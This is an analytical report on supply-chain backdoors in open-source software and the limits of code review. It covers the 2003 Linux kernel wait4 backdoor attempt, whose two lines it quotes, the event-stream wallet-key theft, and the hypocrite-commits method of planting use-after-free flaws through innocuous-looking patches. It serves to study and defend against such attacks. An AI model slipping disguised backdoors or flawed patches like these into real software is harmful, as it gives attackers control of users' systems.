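# Backdoors Built from Innocuous-Looking Commits: XZ Utils, the Hypocrite Commits Experiment and the Review of AI-Written Code

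## How open-source changes are reviewed and how often reviewers find security faults

Open-source software is software with source code (the text that programmers write) that anyone may read, copy and change. Most web servers and phones run on it, and most commercial programs contain some. Its projects accept changes from volunteers and company employees all over the world, many of whom have never met. Projects protect their code mainly through per-change review, in which a person reads each proposed change and approves or rejects it separately.

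An attacker who gets code past a project's reviewers can reach everyone who installs the software. A backdoor is hidden code that gives its author access or control that users have not granted. Planting one in software that its victims already trust is a supply-chain attack, meaning an attack on a program's users through the code, tools or packages that go into it. In March 2024, an engineer found the best-known example in XZ Utils, a set of compression tools present on most Linux systems. The backdoor's author, who went by the name Jia Tan, had contributed to the project for more than two years and had become one of its maintainers. In 2020, researchers at the University of Minnesota had emailed deliberately flawed patches to maintainers of the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, to find out whether anyone would notice.

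Coding agents are AI systems that write, run and submit code over many steps with little human direction. Their code now goes through the same kind of review as code written by people. Whether people or agents wrote the code, the reliability of the review depends on what reviewers can see and how often they notice security faults in what they see.

### From a commit to a user's computer

An ordinary repair might begin when a programmer notices that an image library (code that other programs call) crashes when a file lists its width as zero. She copies the project's repository, which holds its files and their history, and adds three lines that reject such files. She also adds a small damaged image so that an automatic test can check the repair from then on. Before anyone else sees the code, she records her work as a commit, which is a change to the project's files with an author, a date and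 a message. Git, which most projects use to keep their history, gives the commit an identifying string computed from its contents. Git takes the author's name from whatever she typed into her settings and does not verify who she is.

Next she opens a pull request, a proposal that the project accept one or more commits. (Kernel developers send patches by email instead.) Automatic tests usually then check that the code compiles and that the behaviour they cover still works. A second person opens the diff, which shows the lines added and removed, with a few unchanged lines on either side. This reviewer may ask why the check is where it is, or ask for a clearer message. The programmer revises the change and the reviewer looks again.

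If the reviewer is satisfied, a maintainer merges the change. A maintainer is someone with the right to accept changes into a project and often to publish its releases. In a small project, the maintainer is also the reviewer, and there may be only one. Large projects have many maintainers but also far more changes to review. In *Development statistics for 6.19*, Corbet (2026) counted 14,344 changes from 2,141 developers, 333 of them first-time contributors, in one 70-day cycle of the Linux kernel. The busiest maintainer on his list signed off 991 patches written by other people, about fourteen a day. Corbet also followed 5,424 people who first contributed between 2019 and 2022, and found that 36% never appeared in a second release. Kernel reviewers spend a good part of their time judging the work of people with no record in the project, most of whom have no hidden motive.

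Some weeks after the merge, a maintainer releases a new version containing everything merged since the last one. The maintainer marks one commit with the version number, using a label Git calls a tag, and produces a release archive, the packaged source code that others will build into a program. Build scripts, which are instructions that can run commands, carry out the build. Normally, no second person compares the archive with the repository before the maintainer publishes it.

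How the code then reaches users depends on the programming language. JavaScript and Python projects mostly upload a package to a registry, a central service from which other developers' tools download it. Imtiaz and Williams (2022), in *Are your dependencies code reviewed?*, point out that a registry keeps its own copy of the code, which may differ from the copy in the repository. Software written in C usually reaches Linux users through a distribution such as Debian or Fedora. A packager takes the release archive, runs the build script, makes any adjustments the distribution needs and publishes a compiled package. Packagers check that the new version builds and works with the other software in the distribution, but few have time to read every line changed since the previous version. The user's computer then installs the package in a routine update, and the user sees, at most, a new version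 number.

If anyone reads the code closely, they therefore do so when reviewing the pull request. After that, people mostly check whether the software works, and because a competent backdoor doesn't break anything, these checks can miss it.

### What a diff leaves out

The programmer's three lines reject a bad image and release the memory that the library had set aside for it. Suppose that an older function in another file also releases this memory whenever loading fails. Each piece of code is sensible alone, but together they release the memory twice, an error that attackers can sometimes exploit to take control of a program. The diff contains only the new lines and the code immediately around them. A reviewer who knows the library well may remember the older function, but anyone else would have to search for it, with nothing in the diff to suggest that a search is needed.

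The damaged test image shows a different kind of gap in review. It is a binary file, which contains data rather than readable text, and Git's ordinary diff reports only that such a file has changed. A reviewer who opened the image in a viewer would learn little about the bytes inside it. *Evaluating Software Supply Chain Security in Research Software* (2025) applied automated checks to scientists' code repositories, including a search for binary artifacts, on the grounds that nobody can properly review them. Projects that handle images, sound or compressed data still need such test files, often deliberately malformed ones.

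Reviewers never see some other files because they are created only when somebody prepares the release. A tool may translate the source into another language, compress it, or write a file that records the version number and date. Imtiaz and Williams took the ten latest updates, as of late 2021, of the thousand most downloaded packages in each of four registries, and compared what the registry distributed with what the repository held at the matching commit. Of the 24,944 updates that their tool could analyse, 20.1% contained at least one "phantom file", their term for a file that appears only in the registry.

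The rate varied with the language. About a third of updates had phantom files in npm (JavaScript) and PyPI (Python), against 6.0% in RubyGems and 1.9% in Crates.io, the registry for Rust. Most had ordinary explanations. In npm, nine in ten were JavaScript or related files, which a build tool may well have translated from another language. In PyPI, nearly half were machine-written header files, and 7.4% were compiled binaries. Some were clearly accidents, such as private settings files that a maintainer had forgotten to exclude. Imtiaz and Williams were not looking for a wave of attacks and did not find one. But the harmless files make a harmful one harder to spot, because when a third of updates contain files from outside the repository, one more is unlikely to stand out.

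*On the Variability of Source Code in Maven Package Rebuilds* (2026) found the same problem in a small set of Java packages. For 23 of the 28 packages, at least one source file that came with the package was missing from the corresponding commit.

Users run the output of a build, which a reviewer does not see even after reading every line of source code. An independent party can check that output by rebuilding the program from the public source and comparing the results, but the right source can be hard to determine. *No Snake Oil* (2026) compared two tools that try to identify the source of Python packages. Among the releases that both could rebuild, the tools identified different repositories or commits for 186. Some of these differences arose only because a project had moved to a new address. Others involved provenance, a checkable record of where software came from and how its makers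 built it. One tool had relied on a provenance record that pointed to the commit that started the release process, and incorrectly treated that commit as the source.

A dishonest publisher can cause more confusion than these honest projects do by accident, because the publisher usually supplies the package's description, including the link to its repository. *SoK* (2025), a survey of attempts to rebuild packages in scripting languages, notes that tools for finding a package's source do not establish a trusted link when the package's author is malicious.

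### Whose changes get read

Outside contributors need a maintainer to accept their changes, but in many projects maintainers can commit directly to the repository without a pull request or a second reviewer. A project can prevent this by requiring approval for every change, but that takes at least two active people who are willing to wait for reviews. Only 15.1% of the repositories in *Evaluating Software Supply Chain Security in Research Software* required approval from at least one reviewer before a merge. Research software may be reviewed less strictly than other open-source code, so the figure may not apply to projects with paid staff.

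Imtiaz and Williams again provide the best measurement for widely used packages. Leaving the phantom files aside, they traced each changed line in an update to the commit that introduced it, then searched GitHub, where most of these projects are developed, for a sign that someone other than the author had been involved. By this test, every changed line had been reviewed in 11.0% of updates, and none had in 36.5%. The median update had 27.2% of its changes reviewed, but in npm the median was 5.9%. Every analysed update was fully reviewed in 9.0% of packages, while 29.7% of packages had no reviewed changes.

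Updates also tended to be either almost entirely reviewed or almost entirely unreviewed. Imtiaz and Williams attribute this to small groups of maintainers who review outsiders' contributions but not one another's. Large organisations such as Google were more likely to review everything. Even projects that routinely reviewed code let some commits through without review, often changes to documentation or configuration files, which people seem to regard as harmless. Configuration changes can still do harm, because some configuration files control how the program is built.

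Their test could count unreviewed commits as reviewed. Nearly a third of the commits that passed did so because one account had opened the pull request and another had merged it, and a person can merge a change without reading it. The test also missed reviews held by email or in a chat room, which leave no trace on GitHub.

More recent figures look better, but they cover only pull requests. Among projects that merge some pull requests without review, *3100 Opinions on Code Review in an AI World* (2026) found that 8% to 14% of human-written pull requests were merged unreviewed, depending on the type of change. Maintainers who write directly to the repository don't open pull requests, so the figures omit the changes least likely to have been read by a second person.

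The Linux kernel has stricter customs than most projects. Every patch carries a chain of sign-offs from the people who handled it, and Corbet found that 56% of the patches in the 6.19 release also had a "Reviewed-by" tag, which names a person who vouches for having examined the change. He describes that share as slightly higher than usual. The maintainers who applied the other 44% may have studied them with care, but the public record does not establish that anyone did.

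The difference between outsiders and maintainers matters for security. Reviewers may read a newcomer's first patches more closely than any later ones. A contributor who does good work for long enough may be offered commit rights, after which their changes often go unreviewed.

### What happens when reviewers do look

Code reviewers' comments seldom concern security. According to *SeRe* (2026), which summarises earlier field studies, only about 1% of review comments in Chromium, the open-source project behind Google's browser, did so. *SecureReviewer* (2025) cites an analysis of 430,000 comments from open-source communities in which the share was under 1%. These low shares could mean that reviewers overlook security, or that few of the changes had anything wrong with them.

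*SeRe* describes a study of 3,126 open-source projects in which Thompson and Wagner found that projects with more thorough review had fewer vulnerabilities (faults that an attacker can exploit), while the number of reviewers made little difference. Projects that review code thoroughly probably do other things well too, so the study cannot isolate the effect of review. Experiments measure that effect more directly, because the researchers know where the faults are and can count how many reviewers find them.

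In an early experiment in 2013, Edmundson and colleagues hired 30 developers to manually review a small web application for security problems. The application had seven known vulnerabilities of three common types. No developer found all seven, and more experienced developers were not reliably better reviewers. Those who reported more real vulnerabilities also tended to report more that did not exist, which suggests that the developers differed partly in how readily they reported a problem. *Software Security during Modern Code Review* (2022) cites the team's view that manual review may be impractical because finding a vulnerability takes several reviewers. These developers knew they were looking for security problems, whereas most reviewers of pull requests are focused on other things.

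Larissa Braz, a software researcher at the University of Zurich, studied that difference with two teams of co-authors. For *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?* (2021), Braz, Fregnan and colleagues recruited 146 people online, 105 of whom had at least three years of professional experience. Without mentioning security, the researchers asked them to review a change of about 140 lines of Java to a program that manages employees' holidays. The team had planted one of two vulnerabilities in the change.

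Eighty participants got a version open to SQL injection, a well-known attack. The program pasted the user's input directly into a database command, so a carefully worded input could rewrite the command. The other 66 got a version that accepted a number from the user without checking its range, so a user could gain an advantage by entering a negative number. Both versions use input without checking it, but the unchecked number looks like ordinary arithmetic rather than a well-known attack.

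Of the 80 reviewers shown the SQL injection, 52 (65%) found it, but only 14 of the 66 shown the unchecked number (21%) found that. The researchers also planted an ordinary bug, unrelated to security, to see whether reviewers were taking the task seriously, and 76 of the 146 found it. About half of the reviewers therefore missed an ordinary bug in a 140-line change, so the security results don't necessarily show a particular weakness at finding security faults.

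The researchers then told everyone that the code contained a vulnerability, without revealing what kind, and invited those who had missed it to look again. This time, 13 of the 28 who had missed the SQL injection found it, and 7 of the 52 who had missed the unchecked number did. The other 60 people, 41% of the total, still had not found the fault after reading a short piece of code twice, the second time knowing it contained a vulnerability. Some of those who missed the unchecked number had found the ordinary bug and taken it for the vulnerability, so finding an obvious mistake can apparently lead a reviewer to stop looking for a hidden one.

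Reviewers in that study received the warning only after they had missed the fault once. *Less is More* (Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues, 2022) compared separate groups instead. Its 150 participants reviewed a 160-line change that let users register for a web service and contained two vulnerabilities. When a database error occurred, the program wrote the user's email address and unencrypted password to a log file. It also protected stored passwords with MD5, an old scrambling method that specialists have long regarded as broken. One group received no instruction about security. The other three were told that the researchers were interested in security problems, and two of these also received a checklist. One checklist was general and had 22 items, and the other had seven items tailored to the change.

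| Instruction to reviewers | Reviewers | Found the logged password | Found the use of MD5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing about security | 33 | 1 (3%) | 7 (21%) |
| Look for security problems | 41 | 19 (46%) | 25 (61%) |
| The same, with a general checklist | 35 | 16 (46%) | 20 (57%) |
| The same, with a tailored checklist | 41 | 19 (46%) | 28 (68%) |

Each of the two papers misprints one percentage. The 2021 text gives 18% for the unchecked number, but the counts work out to 21%. The 2022 table gives 61% for MD5 with the tailored checklist, which should be 68% based on the counts.

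Nearly all of the improvement came from asking reviewers to look for security problems. The checklists added nothing that the team could distinguish from chance, although the tailored one included items that pointed to the exact faults in the code. Braz and colleagues report that instructed reviewers were eight times more likely to find a vulnerability. That figure is a ratio of odds (successes divided by failures), so it sounds larger than the change in the success rate. With both faults pooled, uninstructed reviewers found 12% of the vulnerabilities and instructed reviewers found 54%, about four and a half times the rate, which is still a very large effect for a one-sentence instruction.

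Many of the misses therefore came from what participants were paying attention to. Those without the instruction often explained that they had been reading for structure or style. One of them, who had passed over MD5, wrote, "I would assume there would be some separate security assessment." Most open-source projects have no such assessment. Lack of knowledge also played a part, especially with MD5, where it was the most common explanation in both the instructed and uninstructed groups.

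Projects should probably tell their reviewers to think about security. But participants in the experiment got that instruction once, just before a single short task, and nobody knows how well it would work for a maintainer who has already reviewed many patches that day. Even when the instruction was most effective, reviewers missed roughly half the faults.

These percentages do not carry over directly to a working project. The participants were online volunteers, rewarded with a five-dollar donation to charity, who reviewed unfamiliar code they would never have to maintain. Of the 522 people who opened the 2022 study, only 150 supplied usable results. A maintainer who has worked on a codebase for ten years should do better on code of that size, but may have less time for each review because of a queue of other changes and a day job.

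A more serious limitation for the question of backdoors is that nobody designed the faults in these experiments to escape reviewers. The faults were accidental, or copies of accidental ones that researchers had seeded in the code, and the reviewers had no reason to suspect the author. Both Braz teams also made sure that everything needed to find the vulnerability was visible in the change itself, so reviewers did not have to consider old functions in other files, binary data or build steps. An attacker can use all of those, and can choose a kind of fault that reviewers tend to miss. The gap between 65% for the textbook attack and 21% for the unfamiliar one gives some idea of how much that choice helps. It would be surprising if reviewers did better against a patient attacker, but the experiments do not measure how much worse they would do.

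Pull requests usually carry their author's name, and *Human Reviewers' Attitudes Toward LLM-generated Security Patches* (Iannone, Camporese and colleagues, 2026) tested whether information about the author sways people. The experiment involved 111 Master's students and 14 professionals, and did not measure whether reviewers can find faults. For each of four real vulnerabilities, participants compared two possible patches and picked the better one. The researchers then told them that a person had written one patch and an AI model the other, although AI models had written both, and let them choose again. Most participants ignored the information. Some switched from the patch they had just judged better to the one attributed to a human, and a number of them said they did so because a human had written it.

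## Two earlier attempts: the Linux kernel in 2003 and event-stream in 2018

Neither earlier attempt depended on persuading a reviewer to accept harmful code. In 2003, an intruder wrote it directly into a public copy of the Linux kernel's source. In 2018, a volunteer took over event-stream, a popular JavaScript package, by asking its author for the right to publish it. The harmful code arrived a month later, in a smaller package that event-stream had begun to use.

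### Two lines in a copy of the kernel

In 2003, Linus Torvalds, the creator and lead developer of Linux, kept the kernel's source in BitKeeper, which did the job Git does now. Some developers could not or would not use BitKeeper, so BitMover, the company behind it, ran a second copy in an older program called CVS. *The upcoming security fight*, a 2003 report by the Linux news site LWN, explains that changes flowed only from BitKeeper to CVS. Developers could download the CVS copy but were not meant to commit new work to it.

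On 5 November, BitMover's founder told the kernel's mailing list that somebody had changed the CVS copy directly. Larry McVoy (2003), in *BK2CVS problem*, listed three unexplained entries in the history of a file called exit.c. All three bore the previous day's date and the username of David Miller, a trusted kernel developer, who denied making them. The earliest added two lines and had no message. About twenty minutes later, another entry removed 58 lines, and two minutes after that a third put 58 lines back with an apology for working on the wrong file. The removal and the repair cancelled out. Perhaps the intruder wanted the history to look like an honest muddle. Only the two added lines remained:

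```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The added lines were in the code for wait4, a function that any program can call to wait for another program to finish. Poulsen (2003) wrote in *Thwarted Linux backdoor hints at smarter hacks* that a casual reader would see a routine check that rejects a bad request. The code appeared to return an error if a program passed an odd combination of two options and its user was root, the account with user number 0 and complete control of the machine.

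But in the C programming language, a double equals sign compares two values, while a single one assigns a value. The second half of the condition therefore sets the user number to 0 instead of testing it. C evaluates that half only when the first half is true, so ordinary calls to wait4 would not change the user number. A program that passed exactly those two options would run as root from then on.

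The error code on the second line was only a disguise, because the computer would never reach that line. An assignment in C takes the value assigned, here 0, which counts as false. Even if the line had run, as a programmer named Chad Kitching pointed out on the list, the next line of the existing code would have overwritten the result. Another reader, Tomas Szepe, noticed an extra pair of brackets around the assignment. Compilers often warn about a single equals sign inside a condition, and the brackets suppress that warning, so whoever wrote the lines had thought about automatic checks as well as human readers. The backdoor was useful only to someone who could already run a program on the target machine, but on a shared server that might be any user.

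### How BitMover noticed

A scheduled job converted the BitKeeper history to CVS on one of BitMover's own machines and copied the updated files to the public server. It then computed checksums of both sets of files (short strings that change if the contents change) and emailed a warning if they differed. This comparison detected the tampering, and McVoy found the cause in the file's history. The conversion software ended each entry with a pointer to the matching change in BitKeeper, but the three entries the intruder had forged under Miller's name had no pointer.

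McVoy saw the warning in the morning, ran tests to check whether his own conversion software was at fault, and repaired the file that day. He said the whole episode lasted less than 24 hours. CVS normally records times in UTC. If it did here, the lines had been public for about 28 hours when he announced the repair.

McVoy first told the list that what he had found was "not a big deal", and he posted the two lines only because another developer asked to see them. Ten minutes later a reader said they looked odd, and fifteen minutes after that Kitching asked whether they were a backdoor attempt. McVoy replied, "Good eyes, I missed that."

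The checksums had exposed the change without anyone understanding the code, and people worked out its purpose within half an hour. But they were looking at two isolated lines that they already knew were unauthorised. A reviewer who saw the same lines in an ordinary patch would have had less reason to be suspicious. A security consultant whom Poulsen interviewed thought the backdoor was indistinguishable from an accidental bug, so even a careful reviewer might have just asked the author to fix a typo.

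An LWN reader credited the discovery to the many people who read open-source code. McVoy, writing as "lm" in *One attempt thwarted* (2003), called that nonsense and replied that hundreds of people could have spotted the change but hadn't. They had only had about a day, though, so we can't infer much about what they would have found in a month.

### Whether the change could have reached a release

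Torvalds told the list that the change could not have reached a release. Code entered a release either as a patch emailed to him, which he would read closely if it touched a core file, or through BitKeeper, whose users had no reason to take files from CVS. McVoy worried that a CVS user might unknowingly have sent in a patch containing the two lines. This was less likely than it sounds, because a patch lists only the differences between two versions of a file. If a developer had started from the tampered file, both versions would have contained the backdoor and the patch would have left it out. The patch would have included it only if the developer had compared the file with a clean copy, and Torvalds would then have seen two added lines. *CVE-2003-1161*, Debian's record of the flaw, lists the distribution's kernel packages as unaffected because no release contained the change.

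Theodore Ts'o, another kernel developer, thought a distribution might have picked up the backdoor if it built its kernel from CVS. He was more concerned that someone could forge an email from a trusted developer and send Torvalds a patch presented as a bug fix that also opened a security hole, hidden among other plausible changes. The University of Minnesota researchers tested the kernel's reviewers with similar patches in 2020. Ts'o had long asked for digital signatures in BitKeeper, so that anyone could verify who had made each change, and McVoy now promised to add them.

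Lemos (2003) reported in *Attempted attack on Linux kernel foiled* that McVoy had kept the disk from the compromised server for later analysis. The intruder was still unknown when Freedom to Tinker published *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* in 2013.

### A stranger takes over event-stream

Dominic Tarr published event-stream, a package that helps programs handle data piece by piece as it arrives, in 2011. In Changelog Interviews' *The insider perspective on the event-stream compromise*, he recalled moving on to a better design of his own within about a year. Event-stream became popular only after that, he said, when the makers of a build tool used it in their examples. By 2018, developers' tools were downloading it between 1.5 and 2 million times a week. Tarr had more than 400 packages on npm, the JavaScript registry. He no longer used event-stream and described his maintenance of it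 as "basically ignoring it".

Then a user called right9ctrl emailed to say the package had been useful and offered to spend a few hours a week on it. Nobody had offered before, and Tarr accepted at once. He gave right9ctrl access to the GitHub repository and to publishing on npm, which are separate permissions. Tarr's *statement on event-stream compromise* (2018) defends the decision as normal for the time, since JavaScript developers had long shared publishing rights with contributors, and adds that "you get literally nothing from maintaining a popular package".

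Two reconstructions, Snyk's *A post-mortem of the malicious event-stream backdoor* (2018), by a software security company, and *A Systematic Analysis of the Event-Stream Incident* (Arvanitis, Ntousakis and colleagues, 2022), give this order of events:

| Date in 2018 | Event | What a reader of the change would have found |
|---|---|---|
| 5 August | A user named Antonio Macias publishes flatmap-stream on npm | A small, harmless package |
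| 4–5 September | right9ctrl makes the first commits to event-stream and releases version 3.3.5 | Updated dependencies, new examples, a readme edit |
| 9 September | right9ctrl adds flatmap-stream as a dependency and releases 3.3.6 | A reference to the harmless package |
| 16 September | right9ctrl removes flatmap-stream and releases 4.0.0 | The reference gone |
| 20 September | right9ctrl adds search keywords | A cosmetic edit |
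| 5 October | flatmap-stream 0.1.1 appears on npm | Nothing in event-stream; malicious code in flatmap-stream's npm package |

The commit of 9 September had a plausible purpose. In 2015 a user had asked for the function that flatmap-stream provides, and Tarr had said he would welcome a contribution. A second maintainer might still have asked why event-stream needed a month-old package from an unknown author for such a small job. Anyone who read flatmap-stream at the time would have found nothing wrong with it. Some accounts obscure this; npm's *Details about the event-stream incident* (2018), for example, says right9ctrl added version 0.1.1 on 9 September, but that version did not exist until 26 days later.

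The malicious version spread without a further commit because of how npm handles version numbers. event-stream specified flatmap-stream as "^0.1.0", and the caret lets npm install a later compatible version. From 5 October, a fresh installation of event-stream 3.3.6 therefore included flatmap-stream 0.1.1. Many other projects also specified event-stream with a caret and had already moved to 3.3.6. They did not move to 4.0.0, because a change in the first number signals that a release may be incompatible with earlier ones. After 16 September, event-stream's current source contained no trace of flatmap-stream, but projects on the 3.3 series kept installing it.

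### What the npm package contained

flatmap-stream also had a public repository on GitHub, and the files there looked innocent. CNCF TAG Security's *The event-stream vulnerability*, from a working group on the security of cloud software, notes that the copy on npm had extra code. The additions were at the end of a minified file, meaning one that a tool has stripped of comments and spaces and given shortened names so that it loads faster. The readable version of the file, in the same package, lacked them. Programs that used flatmap-stream loaded the minified file.

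The added code read two encrypted programs from a second file, which the attacker had disguised as test data. To decrypt them, it tried using the description of whatever project was being built, which npm makes available automatically, as the key. The only description that worked was "A Secure Bitcoin Wallet", which belonged to Copay, a wallet app made by BitPay. A GitHub user called maths22 discovered this by trying the descriptions of one npm package after another.

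In Copay, the first decrypted program checked whether the developers were building a version for release. If so, it inserted the second program into a barcode-reading library that the app used, and restored the original file after the build. The second program ran on customers' devices and looked for accounts with more than 100 Bitcoin or 1,000 Bitcoin Cash. It sent their private keys, which are enough to spend the money, to a server in Malaysia. Arvanitis and colleagues, who went through the code line by line, found that it sent account details whatever the balance and used the threshold only for the keys, although npm's description suggests that it left smaller accounts alone.

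Tarr said in the interview that the attack had failed completely. Copay initially said the same, according to npm, but BitPay later confirmed that the code had shipped in versions 5.0.2 to 5.1.0, and customers had to move their funds to new wallets. Arvanitis and colleagues write that the attack directly affected several users but give no figure for losses.

### A warning from an outdated function

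The attacker had made each stage ignore errors, so that a failed decryption would produce no error message. But to find Copay, the code had to attempt a decryption in other projects too, using createDecipher, a function that the developers of Node.js (the program that runs JavaScript outside a browser) had marked as outdated. Node.js 11 printed a warning whenever a program called createDecipher, and the code that ignored errors did not suppress warnings.

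On 29 October, a developer named Jayden Seric reported the warning to nodemon, a widely used tool that restarts a program when its files change. In the discussion, *Deprecation warning at start* (2018), other users confirmed that they saw it too, and for three weeks they treated it only as a nuisance. One of them posted the list of files involved, which pointed to flatmap-stream's minified file. Ayrton Sparling followed the list to code that looked like a disguised payload, which he reported on event-stream's page on 20 November. The attacker could have avoided the warning by using the newer function, whose name, a commenter later observed, is only two letters longer.

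Tarr could not withdraw the release. A few weeks after the handover, he had given up his rights to hundreds of old packages, including event-stream because it seemed to have a good maintainer. right9ctrl was the only person who could still publish or withdraw versions. npm says it learned of the problem on the morning of 26 November, and it removed flatmap-stream and event-stream 3.3.6 that day.

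The malicious version had been available for 52 days. Snyk's *Malicious code found in npm package event-stream downloaded 8 million times* gives a longer period of two and a half months, which starts on 9 September and includes nearly four weeks when the dependency was harmless. The eight million downloads cover the same period, so they overstate how often people received the malicious code.

### Why the kernel change lasted a day and event-stream seven weeks

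BitMover could treat any difference between its two copies of the kernel as a fault, because its own software produced the CVS copy from the BitKeeper one. JavaScript developers could not do the same, because npm packages commonly contain files that are not in the repository. Anyone who noticed that flatmap-stream's package differed from its source would probably not have been alarmed. Tarr suggested rebuilding packages from their public source and checking that the results match, which would have exposed flatmap-stream. He also suspected that the attacker had been too clever, and that unencrypted code in the public repository might have gone unnoticed for longer.

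The two attackers also had different permissions. The kernel intruder was not authorized to change the CVS copy and had to pose as Miller, so the signatures that Ts'o wanted would have revealed the forgery. In event-stream, Tarr had given right9ctrl's account full rights, so a valid signature on the commit of 9 September would have confirmed only that the new maintainer had made it. Tarr had also trusted right9ctrl quickly, as only five days separated right9ctrl's first commit from the one that added flatmap-stream, whereas Jia Tan contributed to XZ Utils for more than two years before the backdoor appeared.

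## The hypocrite commits experiment on the Linux kernel

Kangjie Lu, an assistant professor of computer science at the University of Minnesota, and Qiushi Wu, a researcher there, tested the Linux kernel's reviewers in August 2020 by sending them small patches under false names. They called these patches "hypocrite commits", changes that fix a minor problem while introducing a worse one.

Wu and Lu's *On the Feasibility of Stealthily Introducing Vulnerabilities in Open-Source Software* is mostly about flaws that other people had introduced by accident and places where an attacker could add more. That work uses far more data than the live test, but most accounts of the episode cover little besides the patches, which caused a scandal.

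### Immature vulnerabilities

A vulnerability usually requires several conditions to be true together. Wu and Lu call a vulnerability immature when the code meets only some of these conditions, and they focus mainly on cases where one is missing. An immature vulnerability does no harm, and bug-finding tools may not report it, but an attacker can complete it with a patch of a few lines.

For their test, the researchers chose the use-after-free, a common and serious type of flaw that occurs only when a program releases a block of memory and then uses it. A program asks for a block and receives its address. When the program has finished with the block, it releases it so that other code can use it. In C, releasing a block does not erase the address. If the program later uses the old address, it will read or change memory that may now hold something else, and an attacker who can influence what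 is there may be able to take control.

One of the test patches worked roughly as follows. A function obtains a block of memory that the code calling it will also use, under a different name. The function then asks for a second block. If that request fails, the function stops and reports an error without releasing the first block. This is a memory leak, a minor fault that an automatic testing tool had already reported. The patch makes the obvious fix by adding one line that releases the first block before the function stops. But the calling code still has the block's address and later uses it, which creates a use-after-free vulnerability. The diff shows only a fix for a known fault, because the later use is in another function. A correct patch would release the block in the calling code, after its last use.

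Flaws like this had already reached users by accident. In one that Wu and Lu describe, the kernel's networking code kept its claim on a device even when setting the device up had failed. The kernel counts such claims and releases the memory when the count reaches zero. A one-line patch made the code give up its claim after a failed setup. This brought the count to zero and released the memory, but a clean-up function then used the memory and released it again. The flaw was in the kernel for five years.

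Kernel developers could remove immature vulnerabilities before anyone completes them, but they generally refuse patches that do so. Wu and Lu quote a rule that a patch "must fix a real bug". That rule applies only to the kernel's stable versions, but developers also told the pair that they fix code only when it goes wrong. They already have too many patches to review, and extra checks can slow the kernel down.

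The paper's attacker is an outsider with no reputation who can submit only small changes and must get each one past a maintainer. Someone with the rights Dominic Tarr gave right9ctrl would not need hypocrite commits.

### Past flaws, possible openings and catch rates

Wu and Lu began with publicly recorded kernel vulnerabilities for which they could find both the commit that introduced the flaw and the one that fixed it. Small patches, which they define as changing fewer than 30 lines and adding no features, had introduced 138 of these flaws (9.8%), all by accident. They attributed most of the 138 to the complexity of the code, but judged 9.4% to be careless and quite obvious mistakes.

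Maintainers wrote 37.3% of the patches that introduced these flaws, compared with 47.8% of a sample of 500 recent small patches. By that comparison, a small patch from someone else was about one and a half times as likely to introduce a vulnerability as one from a maintainer. All 138 cases in the collection got past review, so they can show how reviewers fail but not how often.

Wu and Lu wrote programs that scan the kernel's source to count the places where an attacker could introduce a vulnerability. One found 921 places where the code uses memory that a patch could plausibly release too early. Another found 4,657 places where the code has already released memory and a patch could add a later use of it, for instance in an error message. A separate count found 1,085 objects that two pieces of code running at the same time might use and release in either order. These total 6,663, presumably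 the basis for their claim of more than 6,000 immature vulnerabilities.

Most of these are only places to check more closely. Wu and Lu examined 100 results from each of the two programs before choosing three for the live test, and they misjudged at least one of the three. Still, the whole job took one researcher less than a week. There were also plenty of excuses for sending a patch. Kernel developers had fixed 1,228 memory leaks in the previous two years, and a week of automatic testing on an ordinary desktop computer found another 12.

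Wu and Lu then estimated how often reviewers catch use-after-free flaws. They collected flaws from January 2015 to August 2020, including some that maintainers had spotted during review and others that had reached the kernel. Their catch rate is the share of these flaws that maintainers spotted.

| What made the flaw hard to see | Catch rate |
|---|---|
| It depended on the order in which simultaneous code ran (concurrency) | 19.4% |
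| A function released memory as a side effect | 36.3% |
| The code used two names for the same memory | 38.4% |
| It was in code that runs only after an error | 42.0% |
| The code chose which function to call while running | 5 of 9 cases |
| Baseline for comparison | 56.6% |

Wu and Lu regard these rates as upper limits because flaws that nobody has found yet would add to the misses. But their count of catches must also be incomplete. A maintainer may reject a bad patch for another reason, or its author may withdraw it, without anyone recording that it contained a use-after-free. Counting these catches would raise the rates. The paper also gives the number of cases behind the percentage only for the last type of flaw, so readers cannot tell how much chance affected the others.

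The finding about concurrency is the most convincing, because Wu and Lu also measured how long flaws lasted before somebody fixed them, and those involving concurrency lasted longest. The two measures conflict for error-handling code. Flaws there lasted the second longest, yet reviewers caught them more often than flaws involving side effects or duplicate names.

As one remedy, Wu and Lu suggest that each project's code of conduct include a promise not to introduce bugs intentionally, but an attacker would make that promise falsely. They also suggest better automatic testing, which seems more useful, though they acknowledge that it works poorly on the code they would choose to attack. Drivers, which operate particular devices, make up 62% of the kernel's code, and testing them often requires the hardware. Tests also seldom trigger the errors that make error-handling code run.

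### The patches of August 2020

Wu and Lu describe three test patches, each changing fewer than five lines. One added an error message, one fixed a memory leak, and one corrected a device's reference count. If a maintainer replied that a patch looked good, Wu and Lu would immediately reveal the flaw, ask the maintainer not to apply the patch, and supply a correct one. They wrote that maintainers had agreed not to apply the flawed patches in all three cases and that none had become a commit.

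The public mailing list record differs from this account. The Linux Foundation Technical Advisory Board's *Report on University of Minnesota Breach-of-Trust Incident* (2021), written by a committee of senior kernel developers, lists five patches under two invented names.

| Sent (Minnesota time) | Name used | Patch | What happened |
|---|---|---|---|
| 4 August | James Bond | An incomplete but apparently honest fix | Maintainers ignored it because they knew the name was false |
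| 9 August | James Bond | A copy of an earlier bad patch, citing a testing tool | Maintainers rejected it, with a first reply after seven hours |
| 20 August | George Acosta | An extra error message in a driver | The maintainer accepted it, and it was correct |
| 20 August | George Acosta | An incorrect fix | A reviewer spotted the problem within five hours and suggested corrections, which the sender ignored |
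| 21 August | James Bond | An incorrect fix | The driver's maintainer rejected it after six days, and the sender apologised |

The researchers told the board that the patch of 4 August was an ordinary bug fix unrelated to the experiment. They said it went out under the name James Bond by mistake, because they had already set up a computer to send mail under that name. The board found evidence for this in Wu's attempt to fix the same function in June from a university address. In a reply to the board, Lu (2021) passed on a statement from the computer science department that the experiment consisted of only the other four patches, one of which was valid.

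That leaves three bad patches, at most two of which are among the three in the paper. Biggers (2021), a kernel developer who compared the mailing list with the paper, matched the accepted patch, which was harmless, to the paper's error-message example. Biggers also found that both George Acosta patches resembled code in the paper, and the patch of 9 August cited a testing tool, as the paper's memory-leak example did. The paper probably left out the bad patch of 21 August.

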